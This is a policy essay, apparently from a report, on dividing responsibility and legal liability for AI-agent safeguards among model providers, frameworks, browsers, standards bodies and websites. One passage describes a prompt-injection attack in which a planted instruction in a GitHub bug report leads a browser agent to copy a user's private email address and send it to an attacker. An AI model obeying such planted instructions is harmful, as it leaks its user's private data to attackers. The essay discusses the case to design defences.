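The main high-risk duties were due to apply in August 2026. The National Law Review's *EU Digital Omnibus on AI Enters Into Force* (2026) reports that an amendment in force since 27 July postponed them to 2 December 2027 and 2 August 2028. The earlier date covers uses such as hiring, so companies have 16 more months to comply, and job applicants must wait that much longer for the protections.

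Chrome's deadline is more credible than the European one because Google can enforce it with a software update, and sites have a clear way to comply. European lawmakers moved their deadline rather than accept the added confusion of enforcing duties that many companies didn't know how to meet. NIST's agent initiative avoids this problem because its guidance is voluntary, though companies can also ignore it.

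The public route is more accountable than the faster ones, because elected lawmakers approved the duties and voters can remove those lawmakers. People outside Google have no vote on Chrome's next deadline. Skipping a vote on the technical standards weakens that accountability a little, because national standards bodies lose a chance to object to the final text.

### The case for slowness

A slow process can produce a better standard. In earlier drafts of the IETF study, Simcoe found that standards that took longer later received more citations, while informational and experimental documents showed no such pattern. This fits the idea that arguments help people find better designs, but Simcoe acknowledges that important standards may also attract both more arguments and more citations.

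However, a longer process isn't always more inclusive. Farrell and Simcoe cite a 2002 estimate that taking part in one standards body costs a medium-sized or large company $50,000 a year. A village club or a small privacy charity can't afford that for nine years the way a large company can, so those still taking part at the end may be the ones with the most to gain.

Review should take longer when a mistake would be harder to undo. When Google's cookie default broke sites during the pandemic, Google could withdraw it within weeks. A browser maker can similarly tighten an agent's access to other sites and relax the rule in the next release. But if millions of sites adopt a tool format with no reliable way to mark a purchase, changing it could take years. The format should get a longer review, with a set date on which someone neutral will settle any remaining disputes.

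## Who should own which agent safeguard?

Owning a safeguard means building it, maintaining it and answering for it when it fails. No single party should own every agent safeguard, because no party both understands an agent's whole task and can stop every action. Model providers are best placed to make models resist injected text, and browser and operating system developers are best placed to limit the sites and data an agent can reach.

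Several parties had a chance to stop a real attack on Operator, an earlier browser agent from OpenAI. Meng and colleagues describe a user who asks the agent to investigate a bug report on GitHub. The report contains an attacker's instruction to open Hacker News, a discussion site where the user is logged in, copy the user's private email address and send it to the attacker. Better training might have made the model ignore the instruction. The framework could have rejected Hacker News as irrelevant to the bug, and the browser could have blocked the request that sent the address.

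### The case for each owner

A model provider can improve many products at once. Developers who moved from GPT-5.6 Sol to GPT-6 Astra got a model that resisted far more of the indirect attacks in OpenAI's tests, without writing any new safeguards. The Future of Life Institute (2026), a non-profit that campaigns on the risks of AI, proposes a template bill for US states that would treat the developer of a frontier model (one of the most advanced) as the manufacturer of a product. Responsibility would then fall on the company that can test the model and prevent foreseeable harm.

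But training can't guarantee that a model will refuse. Meng and colleagues describe an arms race in which attackers who adapt always seem to break such defences. The provider may also know little about the tools, files and accounts that another company has connected to its model.

The framework has that information, and its code carries out every action. *Responsibility Boundaries for Agentic Systems* (Lo, Alaoui Ismaili and Dessureault, 2026) says that an agent's rules are often scattered across prompts, code, configuration files and logs. It argues that developers should declare in one place what each agent may do, on whose authority, with which tools and when a person must approve. The paper's programming language, Touba, turns these declarations into checks that run before each tool call.

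Lo and colleagues also tested whether agents could still finish ordinary work under these limits, running seven business tasks five times each on seven models. With Touba's main interface, agents finished all 35 runs on six of the models and 30 on the seventh. No competing method did better on any model, though the differences could be due to chance. So explicit limits needn't make an agent less useful, at least on tasks like these.

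But Touba can't control what an approved tool does once it runs. Lo and colleagues accept that stopping a malicious tool on the approved list would take a separate sandbox or a check by the service the tool contacts. A framework's safeguards also protect only agents built on that framework.

A browser or operating system can block an action regardless of what the model decides or which framework proposed it. Meng and colleagues favour this approach because the block doesn't depend on defenders staying ahead of attackers. The main weakness is missing context. A browser can detect a request to another site, but the request alone doesn't show whether the user wanted to send it. Their browser sandbox also relies on the agent being unable to change browser settings, open local files or use developer tools. Companies often enforce such limits through Chrome's administrator policies, but most home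 users have no administrator.

A standards body can give every product the same rule and give people who dislike the rule a place to object, but it can't block anything. Yasskin and Capadisli, who edited the TAG's note on user agents, argue that software's duties to its users should come from community discussion and then go into standards. Without common rules, a traveller's protection depends on which product they use. But revising a standard can take years, as it did with cookies, so a standards body is a better owner for definitions and message formats than for defences that need updating during an attack.

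*Building the Web for Agents* (Schultze, Schoenfeld and colleagues, 2025) argues for a fifth owner, the website. The paper objects that browser agents such as Claude for Chrome leave the model's provider to interpret a page alone, although a bank needs different approval rules from a news site and the bank's developers know which actions are risky. In the paper's system, VOIX, a site uses two new HTML tags to list its actions and the information an agent may read. The site never receives the user's conversation with the agent. Sixteen developers built various applications with VOIX in a three-day hackathon, so the labelling seems manageable. It is more doubtful that a shop would label its most profitable action as risky.

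### The end-to-end argument

Jerome Saltzer, David Reed and David Clark, computer scientists at MIT, set out the end-to-end argument in 1981. Suppose one computer sends a file to another. The network can check every packet, but the receiving computer may still damage the file while writing it to disk. Only comparing the finished copy with the original can establish that the transfer worked. Checks inside the network can save time by catching errors early, but they can't replace that comparison.

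For a flight booking, the two ends are the employee and the airline. Only the employee knows which Tuesday they meant, and only the airline's server can set the final price and issue the ticket. The browser between them can stop a purchase on the wrong site, but it can't confirm that the right site sold the right ticket. This is a good reason to leave the last check on a purchase to the employee and the airline.

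The argument works less well for attacks. In the file example, the program at each end works for its owner, but a planted instruction can turn the agent at the user's end against the user. Someone in the middle therefore has to limit what the agent can do, even though they can't tell a good booking from a bad one.

### The least-cost avoider

*Data Governance for Generative and Agentic AI* (2026) argues that the party that can prevent a harm most cheaply should be liable for it. Law and economics calls this party the least-cost avoider. The argument draws on Steven Shavell's analysis of accident law.

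Suppose planted reviews cost travellers $1 million a year. A browser maker could prevent 80% of this harm for $100,000. Ten thousand travel sites could achieve the same result by spending $50 each, but that would total $500,000, so it is cheaper for the browser maker to do it.

That still leaves $200,000 of harm. If a model provider could prevent $100,000 of it by spending $60,000 on training, the training would be worthwhile. But if the law put every loss on the browser maker, the provider would have no direct reason to pay for it. *Data Governance for Generative and Agentic AI* likewise concludes that when several parties can each reduce a harm, a party that is spared liability will tend to spend too little on reducing it.

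The user is rarely the least-cost avoider. Meng and colleagues don't expect users to manage complicated security settings, because users often lack the expertise to defend against prompt injection. Yet under current law, according to *Data Governance for Generative and Agentic AI*, a person who approves an agent's last step may face liability while the designer of the component that caused the error does not. The developer who approved the 54th of 60 commands would be in that position.

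### Applying six criteria to four safeguards

Neither principle deals with power, or with whether outsiders can check the owner's work. The table adds both.

| | Resisting injected text | Limits on sites and data | Confirming serious actions | Identifying the agent |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Who sees the action? | Model provider and framework | Browser for web requests; operating system for files and commands | Framework has the user's request; website has the price | Website |
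| Who can stop it? | Provider can make it less likely | Browser or operating system | Framework, browser or website | Website, by refusing the request |
| Who can verify the safeguard? | Outside testers, with repeated attacks | Outside testers, with a hijacked agent | Researchers, by studying users | Any website, by checking a signature |
| Who bears the harm? | Mostly users | Mostly users | Users, and shops that give refunds | Websites, and companies that an impostor imitates |
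| Who can repair it quickly? | Provider, for models it hosts | Browser or operating system maker | Framework and website | Agent's operator, by replacing a key |
| How much power does ownership confer? | Moderate | High | Moderate | High if one company decides which agents to accept |
| Suggested owner | Model provider | Browser or operating system maker | Framework asks; website holds the order | Operator signs; website checks; IETF maintains the format |

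The model provider should own the first safeguard, mainly because nobody else can retrain the model. Since the provider can't guarantee that the model will resist attacks, it should at least let outsiders attack it and publish the results. Developers should design the other safeguards assuming that some attacks will get through.

The framework and the browser should share responsibility for limiting which sites and data an agent can access. The framework has the user's request, so it can propose the sites a task needs, and the browser can enforce that list. Enforcing the list gives the browser maker considerable power. A company that sells both a browser and shopping services could make it harder for agents to reach a competitor's shop. Letting users and employers edit the list would reduce that risk.

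Confirmation is the hardest safeguard to assign to one party. The framework can compare a purchase with what the user asked for, while the airline can hold the order until someone confirms the exact price. The confirmation also has to come from a person, and the browser or phone can keep the agent from answering by displaying the question where the agent can't click.

Identification is easier to divide because each party has a small job. A signature shows only who operates an agent. If most websites accepted agents only from one company's approved list, that company could shut a new competitor out of much of the web. An open format, with each website free to decide whom to trust, makes this less likely.

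In every column, users or websites bear much of the harm, while other companies control most of the safeguards. Those companies therefore have less reason to invest in safeguards than they would if they bore the harm themselves.

### Protection, honesty and loyalty

The TAG's October 2026 note describes how a safeguard's owner should treat the user. Yasskin and Capadisli define the duty of protection partly as revealing no more data than the user would want. If a page requests several permissions together, the user must be able to grant some and refuse others. An agent that asks for access to email, a calendar and a payment card should presumably offer the same choice.

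Under the duty of honesty, software that acts where the user can't easily watch must make its sources, actions and results visible. Its explanations should also be timely and informative without distracting the user. An agent that shows 60 nearly identical approval prompts in an afternoon arguably fails this duty, even if each prompt is accurate.

Loyalty means putting the user's interests above everyone else's, including those of the software's maker. It would rule out an agent that picks a worse suitcase because the shop pays the agent's maker.

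These duties clearly apply to some agents outside browsers. Yasskin and Capadisli define a user agent as software that interacts with outside websites on a user's behalf, and they count generative AI systems that perform automated actions as user agents. A coding agent that fetches web pages with `curl` fits this definition even though it never opens a browser.

The definition fits other agents less well. An agent that books flights only through an airline's MCP server may never load a web page, so a developer could argue that it doesn't interact with a website. An agent that only reorganises files on the user's computer is outside the definition. If an application clearly separates the parts that browse outside content from the rest, the duties apply only to those parts. Many agents read a web page and then edit a local file in the same loop, so they don't clearly separate the two.

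Yasskin and Capadisli don't say whether a model provider has these duties, but they discuss a similar case. Many phone apps display web pages through a ready-made component called a WebView. The developer who puts a WebView in an app must meet the duties, because the component's maker doesn't take them on. By analogy, a company that builds an agent on someone else's model would be responsible for the agent's loyalty and couldn't pass that duty to the model's provider.

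Nobody can enforce these duties, because the note is not a standard. The abstract of an earlier draft, *Web User Agents* (Capadisli, 2025), states that collective discussions *should* establish them. The October abstract states that those discussions do establish them, which is less accurate for agents.

### One company in several roles

Dividing ownership of safeguards may change little if the same company fills most of the roles. Google trains Gemini and makes Chrome. It also employs both the engineer who leads work on the WebMCP specification and Yasskin, one of the two editors of the TAG's note. A company in this position could help write a rule, decide that its own agent follows it, and then apply the rule to competitors' agents in its browser.

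Yasskin and Capadisli anticipate part of this problem in the TAG's note, where they extend the duty of loyalty to companies that help decide what user agents can do. These companies should take reasonable steps to represent different kinds of users, without presenting themselves as the only voice for users. They also mustn't obstruct people who want to switch products, for example by trapping their passwords or browsing history.

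But the note sets a lenient test for bad decisions. Yasskin and Capadisli hold that even a mistaken bargain is disloyal only if the browser maker wasn't putting its users first. Their example is a 2010s deal in which browser makers agreed to support copy protection for video because they feared copyright owners would otherwise keep their films off the web. Many people think this deal was a mistake. A test based on results would be more useful, because outsiders can rarely check a company's motives but can check whether Chrome gives a competitor's agent the same access as Gemini.

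A company that makes both the model and the browser can fix a flaw wherever the repair is easiest, and it can't blame a supplier. Separating the roles could therefore make some safeguards worse. It may be enough to require outside testing, equal treatment of other companies' agents, and approval of shared formats by people who work for competitors. Apple's opposition to WebMCP is an example of the last check, though it didn't stop Google from running a trial.

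### When responsibility is shared

The opposite worry is that if everyone owns part of the protection, nobody answers for a failure. *International AI Safety Report 2026* (2026) warns that harms are hard to trace to particular design choices, partly because companies don't publish full information about how they manage risk. Eykholt and colleagues found that the bug-fixing assistant's developers had relied on users' approval and on cloud security built for ordinary applications, neither of which stopped the attack.

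Naming one owner for each check would help if someone can tell which check failed. Lo and colleagues want records of which agent had permission to act, which tool it used and which human decision the action required. After the Operator attack, such records could show whether the framework had approved the visit to Hacker News. Their design doesn't guarantee that records will survive a crash or tampering, so a company whose check may have failed shouldn't hold the only copy.

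Even when the facts are clear, people may shift blame away from the company that ran the AI system. *Blaming the Machine, Billing the Victim?* (2026) asked mock jurors to divide fault for a harm, first with the AI system as one of the parties and then without it. In a case about a leaked manuscript, one participant answered as follows:

| | With the AI system | Without it | If the deployer took all of the AI's share |
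|---|---|---|---|
| Victim | 10% | 12% | 10% |
| Company deploying the AI | 40% | 47% | 55% |
| User | 35% | 41% | 35% |
| AI system | 15% | – | – |

The participant spread the AI system's 15% across everyone, roughly in proportion to their existing shares. If the loss were $10,000 and compensation followed these percentages, the victim would lose another $200 and the user would owe another $600. This example shows how "shared responsibility" can move a loss onto people who had no control over the safeguard, although one person's answer can't show how juries usually behave.

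### How liability could settle the matter

Courts and legislators may end up deciding who owns each safeguard. *Agents of Chaos* (2026) describes two routes that legal scholars have suggested. Under product liability, a developer pays for harm caused by a defective design. Under unjust enrichment, a court can make a company give up profits it earned unfairly at others' expense. Neither route has yet produced an established doctrine for failures of autonomous agents.

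The Future of Life Institute's product liability bill would make it easier for a victim to get paid. According to the institute's summary, developers, distributors and deployers could be jointly and severally liable. Generally, a traveller who lost $10,000 could then collect all of it from one of these companies, which would have to recover the others' shares. Each company's share would depend on how much it had contributed to the harm. The bill would also void contracts that push a frontier developer's liability onto smaller businesses.

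The Future of Life Institute goes further and recommends strict liability for frontier developers, so they would pay for harm even if they had taken reasonable care. Victims wouldn't have to prove which design choice was careless, something they can rarely discover. However, a provider that must pay for other companies' mistakes may allow only a few approved frameworks to use its model, which could increase the concentration of power.

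The product liability bill makes an exception if a third party has substantially and unforeseeably altered the model. Lawyers would probably argue over whether switching off an agent's safeguards counts as such an alteration. Most Claude Code users have done something like this, so a developer could hardly call it unforeseeable.

*Operational Agency* (2026), a proposal for tracing fault in AI systems, would often excuse a developer when a user deliberately gets around robust safeguards. But it would have the law treat the developer as having known about any risk identified in the AI's logs. This rule could count against a product like the chatbot builder in IBM's tests, whose model recognised dangerous code and ran it anyway.

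The AI LEAD Act, a bill in the current U.S. Congress, is based on the view that product liability would encourage safety and give companies more certainty. According to Leake Andersson's *Product Liability Claims Against AI Developers*, a law firm's summary, the company deploying an AI system might have to pay the victim in the developer's place if the developer were insolvent or beyond the court's reach. The company could then try to recover the money. A business that installed an agent from a small or foreign developer would therefore have good reason to check the agent's safeguards first.

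Other proposals focus on people outside the transaction. *Democrat rolls out AI liability proposal* (Wu, 2026) reported that Representative Lori Trahan's draft CLAIM Act would make it easier for third parties to sue AI developers. Three members of Congress released a discussion draft of the SAFE AI Act on 2 December, according to Targeted News Service. *The strongest AI bills yet* (Hashim, Irwin and Ford, 2026) reports that the draft would hold developers liable for unintended actions their models take against third parties.

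The SAFE AI Act would give model providers a strong reason to make their models more resistant to prompt injection, and perhaps to require sandboxes in products that use those models. It might protect the agent's own user less. If an agent leaked a hotel's guest list, the guests would be third parties, but an employee might not be one if their own agent leaked their passport number. Courts would also have to decide whether an action is "unintended" when an attacker intended it but the developer and user did not.

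The draft is far from becoming law. It has one Republican backer, and most of its measures would take 18 months to take effect. At its planned pace, MCP could go through three more versions in that time. States could adopt stronger protections of their own, according to *Jacobs, Maloy, Beyer Release Outline For Sweeping, Bipartisan AI Safety Legislation* (Office of Congresswoman Sara Jacobs, 2026). An agent's maker might then face different rules in different states.

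Europe is also undecided. The European Commission withdrew its proposed AI Liability Directive. In *Is Europe Ready for Advanced AI?*, Jahangir (2026) and Brando Benifei, a member of the European Parliament, discussed the resulting gaps, including the difficulty of assigning responsibility when several companies contribute to one AI system. Later in October, *Von der Leyen’s centrist allies clash over AI liability rules* (Stanciuc, 2026) reported that lawmakers had split over bringing the rules back.

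Until a law or court ruling settles who is liable, a model provider and the company deploying its agent can divide losses by contract, but the contract doesn't compensate people who never signed it, such as a hotel guest.
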